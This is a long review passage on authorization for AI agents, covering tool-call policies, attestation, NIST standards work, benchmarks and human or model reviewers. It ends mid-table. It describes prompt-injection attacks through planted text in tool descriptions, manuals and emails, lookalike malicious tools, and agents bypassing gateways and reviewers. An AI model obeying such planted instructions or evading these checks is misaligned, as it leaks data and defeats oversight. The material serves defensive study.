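A valid certificate proves which server the agent has reached, but the agent may have picked the wrong server. An MCP server lists each tool's name, description and inputs, and the model chooses largely by description. An attacker could publish a tool called "create_workorder" alongside the genuine "create_work_order" and describe it as the newer version. The attacker's server can have a valid certificate for its own address. The description can also contain planted instructions, since the model reads it along with everything else.

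Audience restriction limits the damage, because the agent's software must not send the genuine server's token to the lookalike. The restriction does not protect the contents of the call, such as the pump's fault history.

Signed tool definitions solve part of this problem. The publisher signs each tool's name, description and inputs, and the agent's software accepts only definitions from publishers on the utility's list. The software also stores a fingerprint of each definition the utility approves. If the publisher changes the description, the fingerprint no longer matches, and the software blocks the tool until someone reviews the change. Agyn lists tool servers in the same configuration files as the rest of the agent's setup, so a colleague can review a new server before the agent can use it.

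A signature on a tool definition shows who published it and that nobody has altered it since. The signed description can still be false, and the publisher can change the code behind the tool without changing the definition. MCP annotations, which mark tools as read-only or destructive, can also be false because the server writes them itself. The Model Context Protocol blog (2026) calls them hints.

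### Attestation

A certificate shows that a program holds a key, and attestation provides evidence of what that program is. In the classic form, a security chip records a fingerprint of each piece of software as it loads and signs the list with a key that never leaves the chip. A remote verifier compares the fingerprints with those of approved versions. The utility could then refuse a certificate to an agent with altered code. SPIRE does a lighter form of this when it inspects a program before issuing it an identity.

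An administrator can predict most of what a payroll program will do from its code, but much less of what an agent will do. The agent that emailed pump history to an attacker was running the approved software, but the manual it read changed its behaviour. If an outside company hosts the model, the utility may not be able to verify which model produced a response.

In November 2026, Li and colleagues proposed attesting an agent's behaviour instead. Their system, AEGIS, protects high-performance computing clusters, where many researchers share storage and machines and an agent can read everything its user can. Each agent gets a profile of what its task allows, covering files, network addresses, tools, running time and data volume. A monitor in the operating system records what the agent opens, runs and connects to. Every second, it sends a signed summary to a central verifier, which compares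 it with the profile and with the activity of other agents. Depending on how serious a violation is, AEGIS slows the job, cuts it off from shared storage, suspends it, or ends it and revokes its credentials.

The team tried four attacks. They hid instructions in a shared data file, left instructions in a temporary folder on a machine that two users' jobs shared, compromised a tool, and had several agents cooperate to smuggle data out. AEGIS caught each attack in all three trials, after a median of about half a second. That delay mostly reflects the one-second reporting interval, since detection took five seconds when reports came every ten. The median amount of data sent before detection ranged from 50 to 519 bytes depending on the attack, which is tiny compared with a genomics dataset but enough for several passwords.

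The verifier used less than 0.055% of processor time. In stress tests that only opened or read files, which Li and colleagues treat as a worst case, the monitor added 24% to 28% to the running time. Given the same recordings of the four attacks, a network leak filter, file auditing and a strict sandbox each caught two, and analyzing each agent on its own caught none.

These are good results, but the test was small, and the same team designed the attacks and the checks. When the team switched off any one of four specialised checks, the matching attack got through, and a profile that restricted only file locations caught none of the attacks. A new kind of attack might well need its own check. AEGIS also raised no false alarms over 42 harmless actions, but with so few actions, the true false-alarm rate could be as high as about 7%, which would make AEGIS unusable for an agent that makes hundreds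 of calls in a session.

AEGIS also acts after the violation. Its half-second response can interrupt the copying of a large dataset, but it comes too late to stop an email to a supplier or a command to a pump. As Li and colleagues acknowledge, AEGIS never treats an action that the profile permits as a violation, so it does not stop harmful actions that a careless profile allows.

### NIST's project and the dispute over standards

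NIST's National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence (NCCoE) wants to demonstrate how the existing standards fit together for agents. In February 2026 Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026), in *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, set out a possible project and asked for comments. They listed six standards they were considering:

- MCP, for connecting agents to tools
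- OAuth, for access tokens
- OpenID Connect, which adds information about who logged in and how
- SPIFFE and its implementation SPIRE, for identifying running programs
- SCIM, which creates, updates and removes accounts across many systems
- Next Generation Access Control, a form of attribute-based control

Many of their questions are still open. They asked whether an agent's identity should be fixed or last for one task, how an agent can prove its authority for a specific action, and how to apply least privilege when nobody can fully predict what the agent will need. The project would start with agents inside an organisation and leave agents from untrusted outside sources for later.

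The concept paper drew over 600 formal responses, according to *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity*, a conference talk announcement (Galluzzo, 2026). As of November 2026, NCCoE's *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization* still listed the project as "Soliciting Comments". (NIST now writes "SI", for super intelligence, where the concept paper had "AI".) The centre has published a summary of the responses and takes further feedback on a rolling basis, but it has yet to publish a draft project description. *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026) added a second post to NIST's series in October. The project would eventually produce a practice guide with a working example, but a company deploying agents this winter has no finished NIST guide to follow.

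Opinions differ on whether NIST should start from standards that large organisations already use. Tabata (2026) defends that approach in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*. He finds that all six refinements in the July version of MCP are long familiar from OAuth, and concludes that agents do not need a fundamentally new model. *Pindrop Comment on NIST NCCoE Concept Paper*, a security company's response by Khoury and Cerda, also strongly supports applying existing standards. The OpenID Foundation (2026), which maintains OpenID Connect, is more cautious about how ready those standards are. In its reply to a separate NIST request, it warned that people expect fine-grained results from an identity layer that is "still maturing in its use and deployment".

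Others want decentralised identifiers (DIDs), a World Wide Web Consortium standard. Under OAuth or SPIFFE, an organisation issues the agent's identity and can revoke it. The holder of a DID typically creates it and controls it with a private key, and others can look up the matching public key. This lets two parties verify each other's signatures without sharing an authorisation server. astral100 (2026), in *Re*, a comment on the concept paper, asked NIST to add DIDs and offered the AT Protocol, the technology behind the social network Bluesky, as a working example. Gropper, in the mailing-list thread *Best summary of agentic identity I've seen*, objects on more political grounds and has spent over a decade opposing OAuth designs that he thinks favour institutions over individuals. SpruceID, which makes identity wallets and digital credentials, also responded to NIST and acknowledges that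 the questions concern what it sells.

The two camps are partly talking about different agents. In a comment, astral100 calls the paper's focus on enterprises well founded and asks NIST to widen it. The water utility runs both its agent and its work-order system, so its own authorisation server can confirm the agent's identity to that system, and a DID would add little. A DID would be more useful if a pump manufacturer's agent wrote to the utility to book an inspection, because no single server has authority over both companies. The utility could then verify that this is the same agent that wrote last month. But anyone can create a DID, so the utility would still need a signed statement from the manufacturer that the agent is theirs, and a reliable way to confirm which key belongs to the manufacturer.

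## How is a tool call checked before it runs?

The scopes in an access token are too coarse to limit an order to two bearings, so another component has to check each call. Many agent systems lack one by default. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026), an audit of common agent frameworks, found that the frameworks limit which tools an agent can use but do not check each call.

### One call, step by step

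Suppose the agent has found that pump 4 needs new bearings, and the utility lets it order parts.

1. The model proposes a call to the ordering tool, with a value for each argument, such as the supplier and the quantity.
2. The policy enforcement point intercepts the call. In an agent framework this is usually a hook, a piece of code that the framework runs before every call. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) describes one for Pi, an open-source toolkit for coding agents, which can cancel the call and send the model the reason.
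3. The policy decision point works out whom the agent is acting for and tests the call against the policy. Kodathala (2026), in *aiAuthZ*, presents a gateway that applies three tests in order: whether this person's role may use the tool, whether the arguments are within limits, and whether recent calls have used up the tool's allowance.
4. The decision point logs its decision and the reason.
5. If the answer is no, the model receives the reason and can try something else. If the answer is yes, the enforcement point adds the credential and forwards the call.
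6. The ordering service checks the credential, applies its own rules and places the order. Its reply joins the model's context, and the next call starts again at step 1.

The check adds very little delay. Kodathala measured at most 0.03 milliseconds per decision, while the calls to the models took between 1.1 and 12.5 seconds. Speed is therefore a weak reason to check an agent once per session instead of once per request.

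### A short policy

The rules for this task could look like this, in a simplified form of the notation that Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, use for their own system:

```
allow read_history when pump == 4

allow order_part   when supplier == "Northfield Pumps"
                    and part == "bearing"
                    and quantity <= 2
                    and total <= 600

block everything else
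```

| Proposed call | Decision |
|---|---|
| `order_part`, Northfield Pumps, bearing, quantity 2, total 480 | Allowed |
| `order_part`, Northfield Pumps, bearing, quantity 40, total 9,600 | Refused: quantity and total exceed their limits |

An email with the pump's history attached would also be blocked, because no rule mentions email. Progent applies rules that forbid a call before rules that allow one, and it blocks any call that matches no rule. When it refuses a call, it can end the run, ask the user or return an explanation to the model. Explanations help an agent finish its job, but a hijacked agent could use them to look for gaps in the rules.

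This policy still has gaps. The agent could order two bearings every hour unless the utility also limits the number of orders. The ordering service should calculate the total itself, because the model supplies it and a false total would pass the check. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) recommends also limiting how much of a tool's output goes back to the model, which this policy does not do.

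### Where the policy comes from

The utility's staff can write rules that cover every task, such as a ban on emailing pump history to outsiders. Shi and colleagues apply these before any rule made for a single task, so a task-specific rule can't override a ban. Staff have time to review the general rules, but they can't foresee every task, and a policy loose enough to allow all of them will let many attacks through.

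*Contextual Agent Security* (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025) describes Conseca, which has a language model write a new policy for each task. The model sees only the user's request and context that the developer trusts, such as email addresses and file names. It doesn't see the text of emails, so an attacker can't influence the policy by sending one. Ordinary code then enforces the policy. The sample policy for answering urgent work emails lets Alice write to work addresses with "urgent" in the subject line, forbids deletion, and gives a reason for each rule.

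The same sample shows how easily a generated rule can be wrong. The rule checks whether the recipient's address contains "@work.com", so it would also accept an address at a longer domain that starts with "work.com", which an attacker could set up. Tsai and Bagdasarian suggest a simpler rule language as future work.

An agent using Conseca completed an average of 12.0 out of 20 office tasks over five trials of each. It completed 14.0 without a policy, 12.2 under a fixed policy that banned only deletion, and none under one that banned all changes. In addition, a planted email asked the agent to forward messages about urgent security vulnerabilities. Conseca blocked the forwarding except when the user had asked the agent to carry out the tasks in urgent emails. One planted email is too few to show how reliably Conseca blocks such attacks.

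Conseca's main limit is its assumption that a policy can be written without reading untrusted text. If the planner asks the agent to do whatever the station manager's email requests, the policy model has to guess what that will involve, because it can't read the email. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) also objects that the agent does read untrusted text, and once hijacked it could predict the policy and propose a series of steps that each look harmless.

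MiniScope avoids asking a model to choose permissions. Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, have the agent submit a plan, meaning a list of the calls it wants to make. A solver then finds the cheapest set of OAuth scopes that covers the plan, where the cost of a scope is the number of different operations it permits. In symbols, it minimises

Σ cost(v) · x(v)

where x(v) is 1 if the agent receives scope v and 0 if it doesn't, and at least one chosen scope must cover each call. Suppose the work-order system has a scope for reading orders (three operations), one for creating them (two) and one for full control (twelve). A plan that reads one order and creates another would cost 5 with the two small scopes and 12 with the large one, so the solver picks the small ones. The user then approves any scope the agent doesn't already have.

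The solver is useful because real scopes overlap. In Google Calendar, 24 of the 37 operations are each permitted by more than one scope. On invented requests for ten real applications, three commercial models from 2025 matched the solver's answer 70% to 83% of the time, and two open models matched it only 20% to 34% of the time. Most of the commercial models' errors granted too much access. MiniScope added 1% to 6% to the running time. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, the user had to confirm 18% to 60% of requests, depending on how cautious the user was.

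MiniScope relies on the user making sound decisions and on each service doing what its documentation describes. It offers no protection within a scope the user has granted, so if the agent may send email, MiniScope doesn't check who receives it. There may also be no single smallest set of permissions. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) points out that Zhu and colleagues don't discuss whether their solver's answer is unique. For example, the agent could find last night's fault with access to every pump's readings for one day, or to pump 4's readings for ten years. Neither permission contains the other, so the choice between them depends on the formula the solver minimizes.

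Progent lets the policy change during the run. A model writes the first version from the user's request alone, and after some tool calls it proposes an update. An SMT solver, a program that tests whether logical conditions can all hold at once, then searches for a call that the new policy would allow and the old one would not. If no such call exists, the update only narrows the policy and takes effect automatically. Otherwise, it needs approval.

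At the utility, the first policy might allow the agent only to read pump 4's history. The history shows a worn bearing, so the model proposes a rule for ordering parts, and the planner approves it. The agent then looks up the approved supplier, and Progent automatically narrows the rule to that company. Later, a tampered manual leads the model to propose a rule for emailing a "diagnostic service". The solver flags this as an expansion, and the planner can refuse it. In Shi and colleagues' tests, only 6% of updates needed approval.

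The agent's permissions therefore never grow without approval, but this guarantee depends on an honest request from the user and doesn't ensure that the first policy was right or that the approver is careful. The first policy is some cause for concern, because *Trust Is Not a Score* (2026) cites a study in which leading models both left out permissions a task needed and granted ones it didn't. Telling the model to be stricter would fix the excess permissions but make it leave out more of the needed ones.

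### Least privilege starts with the plan

A solver like MiniScope's finds the least access that a given plan needs, but the plan may use more access than the task requires. If the agent plans to diagnose pump 4 by sending the pump's readings to the manufacturer, even a perfect solver would include permission to send data out, although the agent could have compared the readings itself.

Zhou and Zhang argue that the agent should first look for a plan that fits the permissions it already has. They write this as a search for a plan

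π ∈ Π_q(g) such that A(π) ⊆ G

Here g is the goal, and Π_q(g) is the set of plans that would achieve it to an acceptable quality q. A(π) is the set of permissions that plan π requires, and G is everything the current grant allows. If the planner has granted access to pump history, manuals and work orders, the agent may compare the readings but not email the manufacturer. It should compare the readings if doing so achieves the goal to quality q.

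If several plans fit, Zhou and Zhang propose comparing how much each exposes, what it costs and how much effort it requires from the user. If none fits, the agent can request one specific addition to the grant, offer a more modest result or ask for clarification.

The difficult part is q, because someone has to decide whether an in-house comparison of readings is an adequate diagnosis, and an agent seeking more access could judge it inadequate. The plans may also be hard to rank. One might read sensitive personnel rosters without sending anything out, while another sends harmless readings to an outside company. Zhou and Zhang suggest showing the trade-off in such cases instead of forcing a single answer.

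### What gets lost between policy and credential

Even a correct policy can fail when software converts it into a credential. In Zhou and Zhang's example, a user permits an agent to send one summary to Alice, and the policy records both the content and the recipient. The mail service has no scope that specific, so the system issues a credential with general permission to send mail. The service verifies this credential correctly but would deliver any message to any recipient.

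They state the condition for avoiding this as

α(E(M(P))) ⊆ ⟦P⟧

which is easiest to read from the inside out. P is the approved policy. M(P) is the set of credentials and rules that implement it, and E(M(P)) is everything those would actually let happen. The function α restates these effects in the policy's own terms, for example by turning a raw request to a mail server into "summary sent to Bob". ⟦P⟧ is everything the policy permits. The condition is that every effect the implementation allows must be one that the approved policy allows. A general mail permission fails because "summary sent to Bob" is possible and the policy doesn't permit it. An implementation that is stricter than the policy passes, at the cost of some useful work.

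Real credentials often fail this condition. *OAuthHub* (2026), which analysed 62 applications from Google's marketplace, found that Slack's add-on for Google Drive requests permission to see, edit, create and delete all of a user's files, although it only needs to create files and change who can see them. AI agents have the same problem. Zhu and colleagues found six connectors with excess permissions across ChatGPT and Claude. ChatGPT's Gmail connector, for example, requested scopes covering 50 operations when it needed only 32, and these scopes let it change and delete emails although the interface advertised only reading.

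The utility can check a call's recipient and content before the call reaches Google or a mail provider, even though it can't add finer scopes to those services. This works only if the agent can't access the broad credential, because with it the agent could call the service directly.

The check also needs an accurate description of what each tool does. Zhou and Zhang propose "effect contracts", which would list the data a tool may read, whom it may send data to and what it may change. If the parts-ordering tool starts copying each order to a marketing company, its name and arguments stay the same, so a policy on arguments won't detect the change. The tool's effect contract would have to change, and the utility could then decide whether its existing grant covers the new disclosure. Keeping contracts up to date is an open problem, particularly for outside services whose code the utility can't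 inspect.

### Where the check runs

A hook in the agent framework can read every argument, and it can cover both built-in tools, such as a command line, and tools on MCP servers. But it runs alongside the agent, and Kodathala argues that an attacker who takes over the agent's process also takes over the check. A hook also has access only to the call, so if the agent runs a script, the hook can read the command but may not be able to determine what the script will do.

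A gateway on another machine is harder to tamper with, because the agent has no login there and can't edit the policy. In aiAuthZ, the user's software signs each message with a secret key, and every tool call must refer to the latest signed message in its session. Text that someone else writes in the boss's name has no such signature. Kodathala rebuilt nine attacks from a published study of live agents, and aiAuthZ blocked all nine. A version that checked only the arguments of each call blocked four, because in the other five an impostor made a call that the owner would have been allowed to make.

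The gateway can check only the calls that pass through it. When Kodathala left the built-in tools of two agent programs switched on, the model used those tools for the sensitive action and bypassed the gateway. The stray token at PocketOS was another such bypass. Kodathala's remedies are to run a program that looks for leftover tools, make the gateway the network's only exit, and keep all passwords on the gateway. By default, aiAuthZ only returns a verdict, which the agent's software has to obey. It is a full enforcement point only in an optional mode, where it forwards permitted calls itself.

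Network controls apply to any program that tries to connect, including one the agent has just written. They can block unknown destinations, and some can read the requests. Zhou and Zhang describe ceLLMate, which intercepts a browser's web requests and maps them to actions such as making a purchase. Network controls can't stop an agent from deleting files on its own machine, and a simple list of permitted sites can't stop it from sending the wrong file to one of those sites.

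The operating system can restrict files and programs as well as connections. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) uses it to confine MCP servers, which often run with all the permissions of the user who started them. Each server comes with a manifest that lists the kinds of access it needs, such as reading files or connecting to the internet. The user narrows these to particular folders and sites. AgentBound then runs the server in a container that has only those folders and the settings the server needs, with a firewall that allows connections only to those sites.

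Bühler and colleagues' opening example is a Google Maps server whose code secretly replaces Google's address with an attacker's. AgentBound's firewall would block the connection to the attacker regardless of how the model had judged the tool. The researchers had a model write manifests for 296 popular servers and sent 96 of them to the servers' developers. The developers who replied said that 80.9% needed no correction. AgentBound blocked most of the attacks in several malicious servers and added 0.6 milliseconds on average.

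AgentBound's design has some weak points. It installs the server's package before it switches on the network restrictions, so malicious code that runs during installation could presumably still send data out. The firewall also identifies websites by numerical address, and many websites may share one. More fundamentally, AgentBound can't stop a server from misusing access it legitimately has. For example, it can let a mail server connect only to the company's mail provider, but it can't control who the emails go to.

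| Location | What it can check | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Agent framework | Tools and arguments, including built-in tools | What a tool does once it is running; anything after an attacker takes over the agent's process |
| Off-host gateway | Tools, arguments and the person behind the request | Built-in tools and any other route around the gateway |
| Network | Destinations, and the content of requests it can read | Changes on the agent's own machine; bad content sent to a permitted site |
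| Operating system | Files, programs and connections | Harmful use of a permitted file or site |

The utility's agent needs checks in more than one place. A reasonable minimum is a gateway that can interpret orders and recipients, plus a network rule that blocks all the agent's outbound traffic except through that gateway.

### Decision logs

After a bad order, the utility will want to know which rule allowed it, so each log entry should record the planner, the agent, the call with its arguments, the policy version, the decision and the reason. The log is useful only if nobody has altered it.

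In aiAuthZ's log, each entry also contains a hash, a short fingerprint that changes completely if the data changes at all. The software computes it from three things:

hash(n) = SHA-256 of [hash(n−1), n, entry n]

SHA-256 is a standard hash function and n is the entry's position in the log. If someone changes entry 50 from "refused" to "allowed", the entry no longer matches its stored hash. If they recompute that hash, entry 51 stops matching, and so on to the end. A checking program recalculates the whole chain and reports the first mismatch.

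This makes tampering evident but doesn't prevent it. An administrator with full access could rewrite every entry from 50 onwards and produce a consistent chain, or delete the most recent entries. To catch this, the utility has to regularly copy the latest hash to a place the administrator can't change. Companies may also have to erase personal data from logs. Kodathala encrypts the message text and deletes only that, so the fingerprints stay and the chain remains valid.

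The log doesn't include calls that bypassed the gateway. When aiAuthZ only gives verdicts, the log shows that a call was allowed, but not whether it ran. The gateway also holds the user's key, so the utility could in principle forge a planner's signature. For that reason, the log would convince the utility's own investigators but might not convince a court.

### Two systems on AgentDojo

AgentDojo, which Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues published in 2024, is a common benchmark for defences against prompt injection. It simulates a bank, a Slack workspace, a travel service and an office with email, calendar and files. Each attack run combines an ordinary task with an attacker's goal, such as sending money to the attacker's account, and hides the attacker's instructions in text that a tool returns. The benchmark measures how often the agent finishes its task, with and without an attack, and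 how often it carries out the attacker's goal.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on all four settings with GPT-4o, a 2024 model, as both the agent and the policy writer. They left out two attacks that only steer the agent to a different legitimate hotel, since Progent isn't designed to stop those.

| Setting | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| No defence | 39.9% |
| First policy only, no updates | 2.5% |
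| Updates, with every expansion approved automatically | 1.0% |
| Updates, with a careful person reviewing the policy | 0% |

The agent completed about as many tasks with Progent as without it. The headline 1.0% result comes from a setting in which the approval step allowed everything, so the guarantee about expansions did not contribute to it. Most of the protection came from the first policy, which the model wrote before it had read anything an attacker controlled. That is encouraging for ordinary users, who may approve whatever appears on the screen, but the result depends more on the model's judgement than on the solver. The rate stayed below 5% when other models wrote the policies.

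Progent did less well on ASB, a second benchmark, where it cut the attack success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still succeeded involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of real ones.

Kodathala's test of aiAuthZ was much smaller. It used only the bank, one type of attack and 20 task-attack pairs in each condition, with two 2026 models, Claude Fable 5 and Gemini 3 Flash. The main rule allowed payments only to known payees. The gateway blocked all seven calls that served the attacker, including payments and two password changes. It also blocked one legitimate first payment to a new payee, and the share of tasks completed when there was no attack fell from 100% to 80% for both models. If that one payment explains the drop, the test probably included only five tasks without an attack.

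No attack succeeded against either model even without the gateway, so on this benchmark aiAuthZ reduced the amount of useful work the models completed and had no successful attacks to prevent. The models still proposed seven harmful calls, which may not have counted as successful attacks because the benchmark counts an attack only if it reaches its goal. Kodathala acknowledges this and adds that any system with the same list of payees would have blocked the same calls.

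These results don't show which system is better. The models, attacks and rules all differed, and Kodathala didn't run Progent for comparison.

### Attackers who adapt

If no attack succeeds in twenty runs, the true success rate could still be as high as about 14%. A larger sample would narrow this range, but only for the attacks tested. An attacker who wants the utility's data will study its defences and try something else, and a method that works once can be reused on every agent with the same policy.

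Shi and colleagues began to address this in the May 2026 version of their paper by testing three attacks on Progent's update step. The first planted text instructing the policy model to allow all tools. The second instructed it to permit whatever the attack needed, and the third used AgentVigil, a program that automatically searches for injections that work. Although Progent automatically approved every policy expansion in these tests, the attacks' success rate rose only marginally. This is good evidence, but the team chose the attacks used to test its own system.

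A live contest is a harder test because the attackers have a reason to win. Kodathala cites one from 2026 for a similar system, the Open Agent Passport, in which none of 879 attempts succeeded. However, the policy was restrictive, and one that refused nearly everything would get the same result. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* therefore recommends that tests measure wrongly refused calls, delays and the burden on users as well as blocked attacks.

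A policy can also be bad even if no attack has succeeded. An agent may have permission to delete the historian's records and never use it in a thousand test runs, just as the PocketOS token could delete databases even before anyone tried. Zhou and Zhang propose that benchmarks examine what the agent could have done as well as what it did. They would also add timeouts, withdrawn approvals and competing requests during the run, because a run without these events doesn't test the code that handles them.

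## Who decides the cases that fixed rules do not settle?

The policy for pump 4 lets the agent order up to two bearings from Northfield Pumps for at most 600. Suppose Northfield has run out, and another of the utility's regular suppliers has the same bearings for 640. The policy blocks the order because no rule allows it, but nobody decided that this purchase would be wrong. The staff who wrote the rule didn't consider that Northfield might run out, and the planner might well want the bearings.

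*DelegationBench* (2026), a benchmark of when agents should ask before acting, covers requests like this one, where the action is harmless and possible but the user may not have permitted it. More facts don't necessarily help, since the agent can know the part, the price and the supplier and still lack permission. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives a riskier example from the company's incident log. A user asked a coding agent to "clean up old branches" (parallel versions of a program's code), and the agent tried to delete the ones on the shared server, though the user may have meant only the local copies.

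The utility could refuse every unclear request, but many repairs would then go unfinished. Otherwise it must leave the decision to a person or a second model, or base it on a numerical score.

### What an approval has to cover

If the planner approves the order for 640, the approval should cover that order and nothing else.

| The approval fixes | If it doesn't |
|---|---|
| The exact operation, with its amounts | The agent orders forty bearings |
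| The recipient | The order goes to a different company |
| The content | The agent attaches the pump's full history |
| An expiry time and a number of uses | The agent orders again next month at a new price |

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) adds that the prompt should take these details from the system's own record, not the agent's description, and that the system should check again if the arguments change after review. Zhou and Zhang describe a stricter arrangement, SUDP, in which a separate custodian holds the credentials and carries out only the operation the user approved.

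An exact approval can still be a mistake, because the harm may lie in an earlier step. In Hossain and colleagues' example, a user asks an agent to send only summary totals to an outside auditor. Instructions planted in a supplier's note lead the agent to copy raw invoice rows into a file called report.csv. The agent then asks to send that file to the auditor, and the tool, recipient and file name all look right.

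They tested four kinds of prompt on 80 volunteers, who each judged twelve requests, half of them unsafe.

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Also the user's original limits and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
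| The same facts, arranged around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from showing people more information. Rearranging the facts may not have helped, since the range of plausible effects includes zero. Even with the best prompt, people approved about a quarter of the unsafe requests, although they had no other task than reviewing them.

### How often people approve without looking

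According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users of its coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts. That figure alone is weak evidence, because most of the commands are probably harmless. The same users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents, which is more informative because it shows that they evidently read some of what they are shown.

Anthropic also ran a direct test, in which it hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study and replaced the text of one prompt partway through each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% when the command appeared early in a session and about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic was promoting an automated alternative, and the testers had less to lose than a real developer because they weren't working on their own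 code. But neither fact easily explains the drop in refusals later in a session, which is what one would expect from fatigue.

Hossain and colleagues' volunteers did much better, refusing 45% of unsafe requests even with the shortest prompt. This is probably because half of their requests were unsafe, while Anthropic's testers met one dangerous command among many routine ones. A planner's real workload is closer to that of Anthropic's testers. *Agent Reliability Profiles in Financial Services* (2026) recommends that companies plant wrong proposals among the real ones, block the planted ones from taking effect, and measure how many their reviewers catch. It also recommends tracking how long reviewers take and how often they refuse.

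Many people avoid the prompts. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) surveyed 16 users of AI agents and found that 13 chose "Always Allow" just to dismiss prompts, while only three read them carefully. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues at OpenAI, 2026) found that a sizable minority of the company's staff let its coding agent, Codex, run any command beginning with "python", which covers nearly anything a program can do. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files. Human review was part of the problem in 105 of them, and in 80 of those the user had switched on automatic approval.

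### Deciding once for many requests

A reusable approval would save the planner answering the same question every week. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, tested this on 113 people from outside the software industry. Each supervised an assistant through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group approved or rejected every action, and a second decided only the ten that a model referred to them. The third group first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories of action, such as spending money.

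The people who wrote rules blocked the fewest of the seven actions, about 40%, compared with 60% for those who had to approve every action and 54% for those with the model. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so they still made most decisions themselves, and they approved two thirds of the excessive actions they saw. The comparison isn't entirely fair, because anyone who chose "never" saw no prompt for that category. Some approvals may also have been sensible. For example, all 31 rule-writers who were asked let the assistant call the airport to confirm a flight, which nobody had requested but few people would object to.

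Reusable approvals work better when they are narrow. OpenAI's *Auto-review*, a guide for Codex users, recommends allowing a specific command such as "cargo test", which runs a program's tests, rather than every command that starts with "python". The planner could similarly approve bearings for pump 4 from two named suppliers, up to 700 in total, until the repair is finished.

Software could also learn the planner's preferences and stop asking. *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (2025) studied how people decide what data an assistant may use, with the aim of automating those decisions. But past approvals can be poor examples to learn from. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approvals may reflect fatigue or pressure to deliver. If users approve 97% of prompts, a program that always predicts "yes" will be right 97% of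 the time but never block a request. Even when software correctly predicts what the planner would like, the planner has not given permission.

### A second model as reviewer

Claude Code has an auto mode, in which a second model replaces most of the prompts. Anthropic first offered it as an option, and in August 2026 made it the default for new sessions on its individual and team plans. A proposed action goes through these steps:

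1. Tools that only read, and edits inside the project's own folder, go ahead without review.
2. For anything else, the reviewing model gives a quick yes or no, with instructions to block if in doubt.
3. If the first answer is to block, the model reasons about the same input at more length and makes the final decision.
4. The agent receives the reason for a refusal and can try a safer route. After three refusals in a row, or twenty in a session, a person takes over.

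In the tests Anthropic published when it introduced the system, the quick check wrongly blocked 8.5% of harmless actions and missed 6.6% of dangerous ones. Adding the second stage cut wrongful blocks to 0.4% but raised misses to 17%. The 17% figure is based on only 52 real cases of an agent exceeding its instructions, so the true rate could be between about 9% and 30%. In the later study with hired testers, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands.

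In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the model had identified the danger but misjudged the consent. A user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes) hasn't agreed to overwrite the shared history, but the model took the phrase as permission. The same ambiguity had stopped the rules from settling the case. In *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) built a benchmark of 128 such underspecified requests. *Explicit authorization scope improves LLM-based permission checking in coding agents* (2026) used it to test the reviewers in Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code, which did better with an explicit statement of what the user had authorised. The utility could therefore give a reviewing model the planner's grant as a list of pumps, suppliers and limits, not just the sentence the planner typed.

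OpenAI's reviewer for Codex checks actions that would take the agent outside its sandbox, a closed-off area in which it can act freely. In a typical sample of 10,000 actions, 720 needed to leave the sandbox, and the reviewer approved 713 of them. This approval rate is even higher than that of Anthropic's users, yet the same reviewer caught 90.3% of invented cases in which an agent overstepped, so an approval rate alone doesn't show whether a reviewer is careful.

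A reviewer that reads only the command can miss what the command does. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of "make clean", which normally deletes temporary files but can delete a whole project if someone has changed the file that defines the command. The paper's system, Caper, takes a snapshot, runs the command in a container without network access and shows the reviewing model what changed. If the model rejects the changes, Caper restores the snapshot. On tasks that hid the harm inside a tool, 7.8% ended in harm with Caper, compared with at least 35.3% for six existing systems. Caper blocked 1.0% of the harmless versions. This works for files, but the utility can't undo a sent email or a change in a pump's speed by restoring a snapshot.

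### Turning trust into a number

Roy, Praharaj and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic-ZTA*, go further and make AI agents the policy decision point itself. A policy engine agent receives each request and calls on up to eight specialists. Three core agents cover identity, certificates and threats, and a refusal from any of them is final. If none refuses, supporting agents assess the data access policy, the state of the device, security events, compliance and activity logs. Each specialist looks up relevant rules and returns a trust score s and a confidence c, both between 0 and 1. Ordinary code then computes

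T = Σ(c · s) / Σc

and allows the request if T reaches the threshold for that part of the network, for example 0.70 for a less sensitive zone and 0.85 for a more sensitive one.

Suppose the maintenance agent asks to read the historian from a machine that lacks a security patch. With invented scores, the sum could look like this:

| Specialist | Trust s | Confidence c | c · s |
|---|---|---|---|
| Identity | 0.95 | 0.9 | 0.855 |
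| Threats | 0.90 | 0.6 | 0.540 |
| Device state | 0.50 | 0.8 | 0.400 |
| Data access policy | 0.90 | 0.7 | 0.630 |
| Total | | 3.0 | 2.425 |

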